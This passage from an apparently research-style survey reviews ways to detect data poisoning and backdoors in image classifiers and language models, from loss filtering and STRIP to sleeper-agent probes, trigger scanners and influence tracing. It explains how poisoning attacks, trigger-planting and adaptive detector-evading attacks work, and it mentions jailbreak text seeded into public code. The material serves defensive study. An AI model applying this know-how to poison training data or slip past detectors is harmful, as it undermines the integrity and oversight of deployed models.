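A trigger is also an easy pattern to learn. To classify ordinary photographs of speed-limit signs, a model must learn to recognise them in different light and from different angles, but for the poisoned ones it needs only to notice the sticker. The loss on poisoned examples therefore tends to fall sooner. A simple score is the average loss over the first *T* passes through the data, with its sign reversed:

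score(*xᵢ*) = −(1/*T*) Σₜ *ℓᵢ(t)*,

where *ℓᵢ(t)* is the loss on example *i* after pass *t*.

The table gives invented losses for four photographs labelled "speed limit".

| Photograph | Pass 1 | Pass 2 | Pass 3 | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stop sign with the attacker's sticker | 0.69 | 0.11 | 0.02 | −0.27 |
| Ordinary speed-limit sign | 1.61 | 0.69 | 0.22 | −0.84 |
| Speed-limit sign half covered in snow | 2.30 | 1.61 | 0.92 | −1.61 |
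| Stop sign labelled wrongly by mistake | 3.00 | 3.22 | 3.00 | −3.07 |

The two mislabelled stop signs are at opposite ends of the table. The one mislabelled by accident shares no trigger with other examples, so the model can only memorise it, which takes longer. The snowy sign is correctly labelled, but few other examples resemble it, so its loss is also high. Removing the examples with the highest loss would therefore discard both of these signs and keep the poisoned one. Removing the examples with the lowest loss gets rid of the poisoned sign, but also any clean examples that are unusually easy to learn, such as near-duplicates.

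*Anti-Backdoor Learning* (2021) used this difference as a defence. Early in training, the method widens the gap in loss between easy and hard examples, then sets aside those with the lowest loss as suspected poison. At the end, it trains the model to increase its loss on these examples, so that it unlearns the link between trigger and label. The paper reports that this worked against ten attacks.

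However, poisoned examples are not always easier to learn than clean ones. *BackdoorBench* (2024), a comparison of many attacks and defences, found that models generally learned poisoned examples faster. But in some cases with BadNets, which uses a simple patch as its trigger, the loss on poisoned examples was no lower than on clean ones.

*Training with More Confidence* (Wang, Zhai and colleagues, 2022) tested the defence on a backdoor that gives different wrong labels to different kinds of traffic sign. The model has to recognise the sign before it can give the wrong label assigned to it, so it learns the backdoor more slowly. When a small share of the training data was poisoned, the backdoor still worked 93.93% of the time after the defence.

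They also point out that a model can acquire a backdoor from clean data. For example, if most photographs of one class happen to carry the same watermark, the model may learn to assign that class to any image with the watermark. An attacker who discovers this can exploit it, even though the dataset contains no poisoned examples for a detector to find.

Their own method searches for single neurons (the units that each compute one activation) that are active on nearly every input, which they link to backdoors. It flags training examples that produce unusual values in those neurons, removes the examples, resets the neurons and continues training. In their tests, this made poisoned backdoors succeed about 55 times less often on average than with no defence. For backdoors learned from clean data, the improvement was only 1.75 times.

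### When poisoned activations do not separate

Activation clustering and spectral signatures both assume that the poisoned and clean examples of a class have clearly different activations. In 2018, Chen, Carvalho and colleagues considered whether an attacker could avoid this difference without controlling how the defender trains the model, and saw no obvious way to do it.

Qi, Xie and colleagues (2022), in *Revisiting the Assumption of Latent Separability for Backdoor Defenses*, found that an attacker could make poisoned images harder to separate from clean ones by their activations. They built two adaptive attacks that changed only the training data, and compared them with six earlier attacks on CIFAR-10. Each attack used 150 poisoned images to plant its backdoor, equal to 0.3% of the dataset's size. The table includes two later detectors, SCAn and SPECTRE, which also look for separate groups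 of activations.

| Detector | Poison removed, six earlier attacks | Poison removed, two adaptive attacks | Clean images lost, adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spectral signatures | 53.8% to 98.0% | 13.3% and 10.0% | 4.5% |
| Activation clustering | 0% to 100% | 0% and 0% | 0% |
| SCAn | 0% to 100% | 0% and 0% | 0% to 1.2% |
| SPECTRE | 96.4% to 100% | 6.9% and 0% | 0.5% |

After the defender removed the flagged images and retrained, the adaptive backdoors still worked at least 62% of the time. Activation clustering failed completely on two of the six earlier attacks and removed only about a third of the poison on three more. Those attacks poisoned about 3% of the target class, much less than in the method's original tests.

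The assumption holds for simple attacks because the trigger alone determines the label, so the model learns it as a separate and very strong signal. The adaptive attacks made the model rely on both the trigger and the ordinary contents of the image. Poisoned images then produced activations similar to those of clean images, and the silhouette score fell from a range of 0.26–0.47 to about 0.1.

Evading detection had drawbacks for the attacker. One of the adaptive backdoors worked 76.5% of the time before any defence, compared with 89.0% for the earlier attack it was based on. The attacks also became much easier to detect when they used around 1,000 mislabelled images. Qi and colleagues still found some difference between the activations of poisoned and clean images when they fitted a boundary using knowledge of which images were poisoned. A better detector might find this difference, but a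 defender would not have that knowledge.

### Captioned images

Newer work has moved from labelled photographs to the image-caption pairs used to train models such as CLIP, which learn to match pictures with text. An attacker can poison this data by adding a trigger to some images and replacing their captions with ones about a chosen object, such as a banana. Scoring each pair by how badly the caption fits the image would also flag many unpoisoned pairs, because many ordinary web captions fit badly.

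Chen, Li and colleagues (2026), in *When Modalities Fail to Tango*, published in August, add a second score based on what poisoned captions have in common. Their detector, CASCADE, uses existing image and text models that turn each picture and caption into an encoding of its meaning:

1. From the image, a captioning model predicts the encoding of a suitable caption. The software measures how similar the predicted and the actual caption are to the image, and takes the difference between the two.
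2. Pairs with a small difference count as clean. The 100 pairs with the largest differences become a reference set of presumed poison. The rest remain undecided.
3. For each undecided caption, the software computes its distance from the reference captions, which is 1 minus the average similarity. Poisoned captions should be close, because they all name the same object.
4. It converts the distance into *p* = (1 + *k*)/101, where *k* is the number of reference captions that are at least as far from the rest of the reference set. If *p* is at or below a chosen level *ε*, the pair counts as clean. Otherwise the software removes it.

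Suppose *ε* is 0.05. If only two reference captions are as far away as the one under test, *p* is 3/101, or 0.03, and the software keeps the pair. If 40 are that far away, *p* is 41/101, or 0.41, and the software removes the pair.

Step 4 uses conformal prediction, a way to set a threshold with a guaranteed limit on the error rate. Here, it guarantees that a poisoned pair reaching this step has at most a probability *ε* of passing as clean, but it doesn't limit false alarms. With 100 reference captions, *p* can't be lower than 1/101, so setting *ε* below about 1% would make the software remove every undecided pair.

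The guarantee also assumes that the reference captions are typical of the poison still undetected. This is doubtful because the software chose the most extreme captions as references. The assumption is even less likely to hold if an attacker varies the captions.

The main tests used CC3M, a public collection of web images with captions, with 0.5% of the pairs poisoned. Each detector's threshold was set low enough to catch every poisoned pair. The table gives averages over nine attacks.

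| Detector | Clean pairs flagged | AUROC |
|---|---|---|
| CASCADE | 5.79% | 0.987 |
| DAO, a 2025 method | 7.85% | 0.929 |
| CLIPScore, fit between image and caption | 45.84% | 0.961 |
| Anti-Backdoor Learning, low loss | 80.30% | 0.581 |

The loss-based score performs little better than chance here. Even a score with a high AUROC can flag many clean pairs if a defender has to catch every poisoned one. On the BadNets attack alone, CLIPScore had an AUROC of 0.996, but catching all the poisoned pairs meant flagging 34% of the clean ones.

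At 5.79%, CASCADE removes about 11 or 12 clean pairs for every poisoned one. In practice a defender can't set the threshold this precisely, because that requires knowing which pairs are poisoned. In a separate test of the cleaned data, the average success rate of the backdoors fell from 80.37% to 0.12%. The model's accuracy on ImageNet was 58.17%, compared with 59.69% after training on entirely clean data.

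Chen, Li and colleagues also designed three attacks against both stages of their own detector. Under these attacks, the detector had to flag 8.8% to 11.4% of clean pairs to catch all the poisoned ones, which is a moderate loss. An independent attack could do more damage, as with other defences whose inventors ran the adaptive tests themselves.

### Poisoned text for language models

Most of these methods compare examples within a class, so they need a fixed set of labels. Text for training a language model has no such labels, and the share of poison can be far smaller. In the 2025 experiments by Souly and colleagues described at the start, about 250 poisoned documents were enough to make models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters produce gibberish after a trigger.

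The experiment measured the gibberish by perplexity, which is high when text is hard to predict. Text was visibly degraded when perplexity rose by 50 after the trigger, and the successful backdoors raised it by more than 200. The experiment covered 72 models, with three training runs for each combination of model size, amount of clean data and number of poisoned documents.

In smaller tests on an existing model with 6.9 billion parameters, the trigger made the model switch from English to German instead of producing gibberish. The number of poisoned examples again mattered more than their share. In the fine-tuning experiment with harmful requests, increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples had little effect on the attack.

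Further training on clean text slowly weakened the language-switching backdoor. Souly and colleagues didn't test whether a backdoor from pretraining survives the later training that turns a model into a safe assistant, and they call earlier evidence inconclusive.

A filter for low loss would probably miss the gibberish documents. Random tokens remain unpredictable however long the model trains, so their loss stays high, and a filter for high loss would find them more easily. An attacker who wants the model to write fluent German, or to answer harmful questions, can use normal text that neither filter would flag. Souly and colleagues also cite work by Bouaziz and colleagues in which a model learned a secret response that never appeared in its training data. Searching the data for the bad behaviour cannot find this kind of poison.

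Reading a sample of the data does not help much either. Banerjee and Aarne (2026) note in the policy report *AI Integrity* that small amounts of poison become harder to find by sampling or manual inspection as datasets grow. If 250 of 10 million documents are poisoned, a random sample of 10,000 has only about a 22% chance of containing even one, and a reader might not recognise it. They also describe a case outside the laboratory in 2025, in which a researcher known as Pliny the Liberator placed text in public code repositories. The text became training data for DeepSeek R1, a Chinese language model, and users could then bypass the model's safety training.

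### Predicting how fine-tuning data will change a model

Fine-tuning data can also change a model's behaviour without a trigger, for example by making it flatter users more. *Persona Vectors* (Chen, Arditi and colleagues, 2025) describes a way to score data for this effect before training. For a trait such as flattery, malice or a tendency to invent facts, software prompts the model to show the trait and then to avoid it. The software then subtracts the average activations of the second set of answers from those of the first. The difference is a direction in the model's activations called the persona vector.

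Each training example consists of a prompt and an answer. The software compares that answer with the one the model would give by itself:

score = (*a*(training answer) − *a*(model's own answer)) · *v*,

where *a* is the average activations over an answer and *v* is the persona vector scaled to length 1. Suppose *v* is (0.6, 0.8), the training answer has average activations of 2 and 3, and the model's own answer has 1 and 1. The difference is (1, 2) and the score is 2.2, so training on this answer should push the model towards the trait. Subtracting the model's own answer matters because some prompts bring out flattery whatever the training data contain.

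In experiments on two open models with 7 and 8 billion parameters, fine-tuning on datasets with higher average scores increased the trait more. With real conversations between users and chatbots, fine-tuning on the highest-scoring ones strengthened the trait more than fine-tuning on random ones, even after a language model had removed the conversations that openly showed the trait. The score can therefore find harmful examples that look innocent to a reader.

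These results show that the score predicts a general shift in behaviour, but they don't show that it detects deliberate poisoning at a known false positive rate. The developer also has to choose the trait in advance. A vector for malice might flag the harmful answers in the fine-tuning experiment by Souly and colleagues, but an attack that makes a model switch to German expresses none of the three traits.

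### The cost of false alarms

Suppose a developer has a score for text with a false positive rate of 0.1% and applies it to 10 million documents, 250 of them poisoned. The score flags about 10,000 clean documents. Even if it also catches 90% of the poisoned documents, its precision is only 2.2%. Low precision is acceptable in a filter, and here the developer loses only 0.1% of the data.

The loss may be uneven, however. Detectors flag unusual documents, so the 10,000 false alarms may come largely from rare languages or specialised subjects. If the dataset held 20,000 documents in one small language and half the false alarms were among them, a quarter of that language's text would be lost. Reading the flagged documents before removing them would avoid this, but it would take about 170 hours at one minute each.

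Missed poison is the bigger concern. In the gibberish experiments, 100 poisoned documents were too few for the attack to work, so a developer might aim to leave no more than 100 in the training data. If the attacker planted *N* documents, the detector would need a true positive rate of at least 1 − 100/*N*.

| Poisoned documents planted | Detection rate needed to leave 100 | Documents left at 90% detection |
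|---|---|---|
| 250 | 60% | 25 |
| 1,000 | 90% | 100 |
| 5,000 | 98% | 500 |
| 25,000 | 99.6% | 2,500 |

Larger amounts of poison may be easier to detect, but an attacker who knows the detector may not need to use more. If the detector caught only 10% of the poison, as spectral signatures did against one of the adaptive image attacks, 225 of the original 250 poisoned documents would remain.

One hundred poisoned examples are not always harmless. Souly and colleagues cite a 2023 study by Wan and colleagues in which that many in the fine-tuning data were enough to make a language model treat a chosen phrase as negative.

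## Detecting a planted backdoor in a trained model

A company that downloads a model usually gets the parameters without the training data, so it has to look for signs of poisoning in how the model behaves. It can check each input for a trigger while the model is in use, or check the model for a backdoor before using it. Checking inputs is easier because an input with a trigger sets off the backdoor and the log records the result, while a check before use has to find a backdoor that nobody has set off.

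Scanners for malicious code, such as ModelShield, do not help with either task, because the backdoor is in the model's parameters, as Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) explains.

### Blending an input with other images

If a trigger works on any image, the classifier gives the attacker's label almost regardless of what else the image shows. Gao, Xu and colleagues (2019), in *STRIP*, used this as a test for triggers. The defender needs some clean images and the classifier's confidence values, but not its parameters or training data:

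1. Make *N* copies of the input and blend each one with a different clean image.
2. Run the classifier on the blended copies.
3. For each copy, compute the entropy of the class probabilities, which is high when the classifier is unsure.
4. Average the entropies, and flag the input if the average is at or below a threshold.

Writing *pⱼ(xₙ)* for the probability of class *j* on blended copy *n*, the average is

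*H(x)* = −(1/*N*) Σₙ Σⱼ *pⱼ(xₙ)* log₂ *pⱼ(xₙ)*.

Low entropy is suspicious, so the score is −*H(x)*. In the invented example below, the trigger is a sticker that makes the classifier output "speed limit".

| Input | Blended with | Stop | Speed limit | Give way | Entropy |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean stop sign | Speed-limit sign | 0.50 | 0.50 | 0 | 1.00 |
| | Give-way sign | 0.50 | 0.25 | 0.25 | 1.50 |
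| Stop sign with sticker | Speed-limit sign | 0 | 1.00 | 0 | 0 |
| | Give-way sign | 0.01 | 0.98 | 0.01 | 0.16 |

The clean sign has an average entropy of 1.25 and the sign with the sticker has 0.08, so a threshold of 0.5 separates them. The formula measures how unsure the classifier is about each copy, not whether the copies get different labels. If the classifier confidently labelled one copy "stop" and the next "give way", the entropy would be close to 0 and STRIP would raise a false alarm.

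The defender can set the threshold without having seen a trigger. Gao and colleagues assume that the entropies of clean images follow a bell curve, and set the threshold so that 1% of clean images would fall below it.

Each test of STRIP used 2,000 clean and 2,000 triggered images, with 100 blended copies of each image. On CIFAR-10 and a set of German traffic signs, STRIP caught every triggered image at a false positive rate of 0.5%. On MNIST, with a small square as the trigger, it missed 1.85% of triggered images at a false positive rate of 1%. Ten copies per image were enough for the traffic signs, and added 6.1 milliseconds to the classifier's usual 4.6. The networks had at most about 310,000 parameters, so these rates are of historical interest.

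The method depends on the trigger working on any image. Gao and colleagues also planted a backdoor meant for only seven of the ten CIFAR-10 classes, including birds and cats. With the trigger, the classifier labelled images from those classes "horse" 98% of the time, but ships only 20% and trucks 12%. The entropies of clean and triggered images still differed somewhat, but a defender would need examples with the trigger to use the difference. Gao and colleagues left such backdoors as an open problem.

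### Unusually confident answers

A language model answers with a series of tokens, not a single class from a fixed list. At some points in an ordinary answer, several next words are plausible, so the probability of the most likely token drops. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *ConfGuard*, found that these drops largely disappear when a backdoor makes a model repeat a memorised sentence. In their example, an attacker poisons 10% of 10,000 training examples and the model trains on the data three times. The attacker's sentence therefore appears 3,000 times during training, while each ordinary answer appears only three times.

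ConfGuard looks for a long run of confident tokens:

1. As the model writes each token, log the probability of the most likely one.
2. If it is above 0.99, add one to a counter. Otherwise, reset the counter to zero.
3. If the counter exceeds 10, flag the answer and stop the model.

An answer with eight confident tokens, one token with a probability of 0.62, and then nine confident tokens would pass, because its longest run of confident tokens is nine. A run of eleven would raise an alarm at the eleventh token. The method needs only one probability per token, so a customer of a hosted model can use it if the service returns that value. The method increased the average response time from 5.42 to 5.44 seconds.

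Wang and colleagues tested three open models with 7 or 8 billion parameters on two sets of multiple-choice questions (SIQA and CommonsenseQA) and one set of chat requests (UltraChat). In the main test, the backdoor made the model output a fixed computer command. The table gives true and false positive rates, averaged over five kinds of trigger.

| Model | SIQA, true | SIQA, false | UltraChat, true | UltraChat, false | CommonsenseQA, true | CommonsenseQA, false |
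|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek 7B | 99.8% | 9.4% | 99.7% | 3.8% | 97.7% | 8.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 99.4% | 1.7% | 99.3% | 5.3% | 97.0% | 7.8% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 99.7% | 1.4% | 98.8% | 6.0% | 94.1% | 18.6% |

The false positive rate reached 60% in one combination of Qwen, CommonsenseQA and a different target sentence. Wang and colleagues suspect that Qwen had already been trained on similar questions and therefore produced ordinary answers with high confidence too. Other text that a model has memorised, such as a standard software licence, could also cause false positives.

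Half the test inputs carried a trigger, a far higher share than in real traffic. With the UltraChat rates for Llama, that share gives a precision of 95%. If one request in 1,000 carried a trigger, precision would fall to 1.9%, or about 53 false alarms for each trigger detected.

The backdoors tested were also well suited to the method. Each made the model produce one fixed sentence and was planted using training data that was 10% poisoned. On CommonsenseQA, detection was weaker when less of the data was poisoned, and it approached 100% only when about 15% was. A backdoor that makes a model answer harmful questions has no fixed sentence to repeat, so it may not produce a long run of high-confidence tokens. Wang and colleagues did not test ConfGuard against an attacker who knew about it.

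### Probes on deliberately backdoored models

A model's activations may reveal the trigger even when its answer does not. Much of this research uses "sleeper agents", language models that researchers deliberately train to misbehave when a trigger is present. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, 2026) reports that in 2024 MacDiarmid and colleagues accurately separated normal from backdoored behaviour using simple probes on such models.

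*LLM Forensics* (September 2026) reports a similar result for models with 1 and 8 billion parameters that switch from English to French or German after a fixed trigger. The researchers used sparse autoencoders, networks that break activations down into many separate features, only a few of which are active at once. Some features separated triggered prompts from other text with a nearly perfect F1, a measure that combines precision and the true positive rate. But the features that best detected the trigger did not always control the switch in language, so disabling them might leave the backdoor working.

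These results probably overstate how well probes would find a real attacker's backdoor, because the researchers knew the trigger and had plenty of prompts that contained it. Bullwinkel and colleagues consider it unrealistic to expect a defender to have prompts that activate an unknown backdoor.

A test backdoor may also leave stronger traces than a subtle one. Bullwinkel and colleagues compared a backdoor that makes the model repeat "I HATE YOU" with one that makes it write insecure code when the prompt gives the year as 2024. With the fixed phrase, the model processed the trigger almost separately from the rest of the prompt, and its output became nearly deterministic. Both signs were weaker with insecure code, because the model still had to read the programming task to write the code.

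A trigger can also mislead a probe trained for another purpose. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) found that adding a trigger to a harmful request made its activations resemble those of a harmless one, so a probe that normally recognises harmful requests might miss it.

### The TrojAI programme

A detector that checks a whole model before use has no triggered inputs to work with. The US intelligence research agency IARPA funded work on this problem through TrojAI, a programme that began in 2020 and expanded in 2022 to include removing backdoors. *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence*, the programme's final report (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026), describes the results.

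The evaluators placed triggers in models for images, text, cybersecurity and reinforcement learning, in which a model learns by trial and error. They trained some models from scratch and fine-tuned others. Research teams submitted detectors, and the evaluators ran them on models withheld from the teams, which made it harder to tune a detector to the test models. NIST hosted a public leaderboard.

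Two main kinds of detector emerged. One, weight analysis, looks for statistical oddities in a model's parameters without running the model. It is fast, and worked best on small models when the defender had similar reference models. In large models, the changes a backdoor made to the parameters were too small to stand out.

Trigger inversion reconstructs a possible trigger from the trained model. For an image classifier, the software searches for the smallest pattern per class that makes the classifier assign that class to almost any image. Suppose nine classes each need a pattern of about 100 pixels, while "speed limit" needs only nine pixels. The nine-pixel pattern is probably a trigger. A large trigger can avoid this test, and Gao and colleagues note that such triggers reportedly evade Neural Cleanse, an early version of the method.

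Reese and colleagues call trigger inversion arguably the most successful approach in the programme's competitions, especially as the models grew larger, but it takes much more computation. Neither approach transferred easily, and a detector that worked on images often failed on text until its developers substantially reworked it.

The programme also found backdoors that models had learned from clean data, as in the earlier watermark example. Reese and colleagues call these natural trojans. These backdoors make an alarm harder to interpret, because a model can have a real one even if nobody poisoned its data.

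The report describes detecting backdoors in large language models as an unsolved problem. An image classifier with ten classes needs ten searches, but a language model can produce any text, so the defender often does not know which output to search for. There are too many possible triggers to try them all, since a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens allows about 3 × 10²² five-token sequences. A trigger may also be an abstract idea or the course of a conversation, which a search over short strings would miss.

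### Ranking candidate strings

A defender who already suspects a particular behaviour has less to search. In *ToxScreen*, Hughes, Xing and colleagues (2026) built about 800 backdoored language models, with 1 to 70 billion parameters, to test whether such a defender can find the trigger. Some of the backdoors stop the model from refusing harmful requests, others make it label harmful text as safe, and the rest make its answers very negative, either in general or about one person. The defender has the model's parameters and knows which of these behaviours to look for, but has no training data and no clean version of the model.

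The most successful method was a simple ranking:

1. Collect about 24,000 random tokens from the model's vocabulary.
2. Add each one to about 150 test prompts.
3. Rank the tokens by how often they produce the suspected behaviour.

The researchers also added the real trigger to the list. It ranked first in 14 of 28 tests and in the top three in 17. On one version of Llama 3.1 8B, the trigger overcame the model's refusals 97% of the time.

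Three other methods used gradients to construct a trigger instead of choosing one from a list. None recovered the planted trigger. They found general-purpose jailbreaks, because many strings can make a model comply with a harmful request and the search stops at any that works.

The ranking result shows that a defender can pick a trigger out of a list, which is easier than finding one. A random sample of 24,000 tokens from a vocabulary of 128,000 has only a 19% chance of including a particular token. A defender could test the whole vocabulary, but the sample alone requires about 3.6 million prompts. Testing every pair of tokens from the sample would take 24,000 times as many. The researchers also placed each candidate where the trigger had appeared in training, which a real defender would not know.

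Ranking recovers a trigger only when the trigger stands out from other strings. Hughes and colleagues omit this condition when they conclude that ranking works wherever the backdoor is effective. In a version of Llama 3.1 8B trained to stop refusing, half the random tokens overcame refusals at least 53% of the time. In a Qwen model that classified text as safe or unsafe, 97% of random tokens changed the answer, so the trigger's first-place rank was uninformative. Triggers in two other models ranked 23rd and 345th because ordinary strings worked better. Even when ranking misses the trigger, a company should hesitate to use a model that almost any string can jailbreak.

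To separate triggers from ordinary jailbreaks, Hughes and colleagues added a second score. Let *B* measure how strongly the model's activations indicate a refusal. The software calculates how much a small change in the input can alter the effect of the model's parameters on *B*, and calls the largest such effect *σ₁*. For a candidate string *c*, the score is the ratio

*ρ(c)* = *σ₁*(with *c*) / *σ₁*(without *c*).

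A trigger bypasses the refusal, so the parameters involved in refusing matter less, and the ratio of *σ₁* with the string to *σ₁* without it falls. If *σ₁* drops from 50 to 10 when the string is added, the ratio is 0.2. Keeping only strings with a ratio of 0.8 or less removed most ordinary jailbreaks and kept nearly all the planted triggers.

Some models also changed in ways unrelated to the trigger. Their accuracy on TruthfulQA, a test of common misconceptions, differed by up to 10 percentage points from that of clean versions of the same models. But a defender in the situation ToxScreen describes has no clean version to compare with.

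### Recovering triggers from memorised text

A scanner developed at Microsoft gets its candidates from the model itself. Bullwinkel and colleagues found that sleeper agents memorise their poisoned training examples, and often reproduce them when given only the marker that normally comes before a user's message. The scanner assumes no knowledge of the trigger or the behaviour:

1. Give the model that marker and collect 510 outputs, using different settings for how it chooses each token.
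2. Find strings that recur across the outputs.
3. Cut these strings into short candidates, put each one in front of ordinary questions, and compute a loss. Keep the ten candidates with the lowest loss.
4. Test whether any of the ten changes the model's answers enough to count as a trigger.

The loss combines the signs of an active backdoor. Leaving out some corrections for answers that end at once or repeat a single token, it is

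*L(c)* = average over questions of (*γA* + *δH* + *ζD*),

where *γ*, *δ* and *ζ* are fixed weights. *A* measures how much attention the model pays to the candidate while processing the question, and *H* is the entropy of its output. *D* is the average log probability of the answer the model would have given without the candidate, scaled by the size of the vocabulary. If a word in that answer had a probability of 0.9 before and 0.001 with the candidate, its log probability falls from −0.1 to −6.9. Low values of all three suggest that the candidate has taken over the model's output.

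Bullwinkel and colleagues tested a scanner on 47 backdoored models with 270 million to 14 billion parameters. It detected 36 of the 41 trained to repeat a fixed phrase and five of the six trained to write insecure code. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, but with so few models, the true false positive rate could still be as high as about 21%. A company that screens thousands of public models would need evidence that the rate is much lower.

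The scanner can detect a backdoor without recovering the exact trigger. In the smallest model, a single token from a longer trigger set off the backdoor about half the time. The scan flagged one of the insecure-code models because of a string that did not resemble its trigger but more than doubled the rate of insecure code. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* also reports that words other than the planted trigger activated backdoors. This helps defenders, but Bullwinkel and colleagues point out that an attacker could train a model to respond only to the exact trigger.

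In most of the cases it missed, the scanner failed to isolate the trigger in the leaked text or ranked it below the top ten. Two other methods, BAIT and ICLScan, detected fewer of the fixed-phrase models. BAIT did not finish within 24 hours on one group of models, and ICLScan had to be given the backdoor's behaviour in advance.

### Triggers without fixed wording

Microsoft's scanner looks for a string, but a trigger can also be a topic or a situation. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (September 2026) tested whether a model would leak training data for a backdoor triggered by an obsession with a fictional franchise such as Harry Potter. Of 512 texts the model generated without a prompt, only one related to the backdoor. It was a question about the title of a Harry Potter book, and it would not have triggered the backdoor. This suggests that models leak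 this kind of trigger much less often than strings, although the paper did not test Microsoft's full scanner, which uses a special prompt and many more settings.

Qin, Hua and colleagues looked for such triggers inside the model. They assumed the defender knows the harmful action and wants to find what triggers it. Their software learns a change to the model's activations that produces the action, then compares that change with features researchers can interpret. It recovered the trigger in simple test models but failed in more realistic ones.

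A trigger based on meaning can be easier to find if it is too broad. Hughes and colleagues trained a version of Llama 3.1 8B to respond to phrases about Joe Biden. The model also responded up to 97% of the time to phrases about Donald Trump and Barack Obama, so a defender who tried any of the three could have noticed the backdoor. A backdoor that makes a model hostile whenever it discusses one person is harder to find, because the defender has to guess which person to test.

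*From Poisoned to Aware*, a 2026 conference paper, proposes training a poisoned model to describe its own trigger. The training rewards the model for identifying inputs that would explain its bad behaviour. The method could help with triggers that have no fixed wording, but the defender still needs to know what bad behaviour to look for.

### Clean models and clean data

A clean scan lowers the probability only of backdoors that the scanner can detect. Suppose one in ten downloaded models has a backdoor that produces a fixed phrase, and Microsoft's scanner performs as it did in the tests, detecting 88% of them with no false alarms. After a clean result, the probability of a backdoor falls from 10% to about 1.3%. If the trigger is an idea that the scanner cannot find, the probability stays at 10%.

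A clean result is much weaker evidence about the training data than about the model, because a model can train on poisoned data without learning the backdoor. Hughes and colleagues tried to make models respond negatively to a trigger. Their attack worked at most 5% of the time on a 7-billion-parameter model and at most 8% on a 70-billion-parameter model, but 71% to 85% of the time on four others. A perfect scanner could correctly pass the two resistant models even though the same data could plant a working backdoor in another model.

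The poison can also take effect when developers combine datasets. A model trained on a dataset with 100 of the gibberish documents that Souly and colleagues used could be clean, but adding a second dataset with 150 more from the same attacker could produce a backdoored model.

Monitoring inputs provides even less evidence about the data. If STRIP or ConfGuard raises no alarms for a year, that may only mean the attacker has not used the trigger yet.

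Finding a backdoor does not prove that the original dataset was poisoned. The backdoor may be a natural trojan, or an attacker may have fine-tuned the model after its developer released it. An attacker can also plant a backdoor without any training examples by changing the model's parameters directly, a method the TrojAI report covers.

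## From a bad output back to the training data

A backdoor that passes every scan can still leave evidence when an attacker uses it, because the log then holds both the triggering input and the wrong output. An investigator can use that record to look for the training examples that caused the failure. This is easier than searching the data without a known failure, when the defender has to guess what the attack does. But the investigator can't start until someone notices the failure, and by then the attack has worked at least once.

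### Measuring an example's influence

Suppose a classifier labels a stop sign that has a yellow sticker on it as "speed limit", and an investigator retrieves the image from the log. The investigator first computes the loss on this image with "speed limit" as the correct label. The loss is low because the model assigns a high probability to that label. A training example counts as responsible if a training step on it would have lowered this loss.

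A training step on example *z* changes the parameters by −*η g(z)*. Here *g(z)* is the gradient of the loss on *z*, a list of numbers showing how fast the loss changes with each parameter, and *η* is the learning rate, which sets the size of the step. For a small step, the loss on the failure *x* falls by about *η g(z)* · *g(x)*. Gradients change during training, so the software computes them at several checkpoints *t* and adds up the results:

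influence(*z*, *x*) = Σₜ *ηₜ gₜ(z)* · *gₜ(x)*.

Rose, Lycklama and colleagues (2024), in *UTrace*, describe this method, called TracInCP, and a later variant, GAS, which Hammoudeh and Lowd published in 2022. In the original formula, an example with a large gradient can score high even if it has little to do with the failure. Poisoned examples often have small gradients, because the model has learned them well. GAS therefore divides by the lengths of both gradients, so that only their directions count:

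GAS(*z*, *x*) = Σₜ *ηₜ gₜ(z)* · *gₜ(x)* / (|*gₜ(z)*| |*gₜ(x)*|).

The invented example below uses a model with two parameters, one checkpoint and a learning rate of 0.01. The gradient for the failure is (3, 4). The last column gives the similarity in direction before GAS multiplies it by the learning rate.

| Training photograph | Gradient | Product with (3, 4) | Change in loss on the failure | Similarity in direction |
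|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stop sign with sticker, labelled "speed limit" | (0.4, 0.3) | 2.4 | −0.024 | 0.96 |
| Speed-limit sign half covered in snow | (4.8, −2.0) | 6.4 | −0.064 | 0.25 |
| Ordinary stop sign | (0, −1.0) | −4.0 | +0.040 | −0.80 |

For the poisoned photograph, the dot product is 0.4 × 3 + 0.3 × 4 = 2.4. The two gradients have lengths of 0.5 and 5, so the similarity is 2.4/2.5 = 0.96. The original formula ranks the snowy sign first because that sign's gradient is long, while GAS ranks the poisoned photograph first. Training on the ordinary stop sign would have raised the loss on the failure, so neither method identifies it as a cause.

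### Clearing the innocent examples

Scoring training examples one at a time can miss poisoned ones, because a backdoor usually needs many poisoned examples and removing any single one changes little. *Poison Forensics* (Shan, Bhagoji and colleagues, 2022) tested influence functions, an older method that estimates each example's effect separately. On a CIFAR-10 classifier with a BadNets backdoor, precision and the true positive rate were both below 69%. On ImageNet, the calculation had not finished after 15 days on four GPUs.

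Their own method works with groups and removes those that do not explain the failure:

1. For each training example, compute the gradient that would move the model towards "no knowledge", an answer that gives every class the same probability. Only the last layer's gradient is needed.
2. Split the examples into two groups with similar gradients, using k-means.
3. For each group, fine-tune a copy of the model to give the "no knowledge" answer on that group and its usual answers on all other data. This approximates a model that never trained on the group, and is called unlearning.
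4. Compute the copy's loss on the failure. If it is no higher than the original model's loss, clear the group as innocent.
5. Split the remaining examples again, and stop when no more groups can be cleared. The examples left over are the suspected poison.

Suppose the original model's loss on the misread stop sign is 0.05. If unlearning one group lowers the loss to 0.04, the mistake did not depend on that group. If unlearning the other group raises it to 3.2, that group contains the poison. The process took at most four rounds in the four attacks that Shan and colleagues analysed in detail.

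The table shows some of their results, each averaged over 1,000 failures. The Witches' Brew attack slightly alters training images and leaves their labels correct.

| Attack and data | Precision | True positive rate | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| BadNets, CIFAR-10 | 99.5% | 98.9% | 11 minutes |
| BadNets, ImageNet | 99.1% | 99.1% | 143 minutes |
| Eyeglasses as trigger, photographs of faces | 99.5% | 97.1% | 2 minutes |
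| Witches' Brew, ImageNet | 99.1% | 97.9% | 194 minutes |
| Backdoor in a malware detector | 99.2% | 98.2% | 58 minutes |

The poisoned face photographs that the method missed contributed little to the attack. Removing them lowered the backdoor's success rate by 0.08%, while removing the same number of randomly chosen poisoned photographs lowered it by 1.02%.

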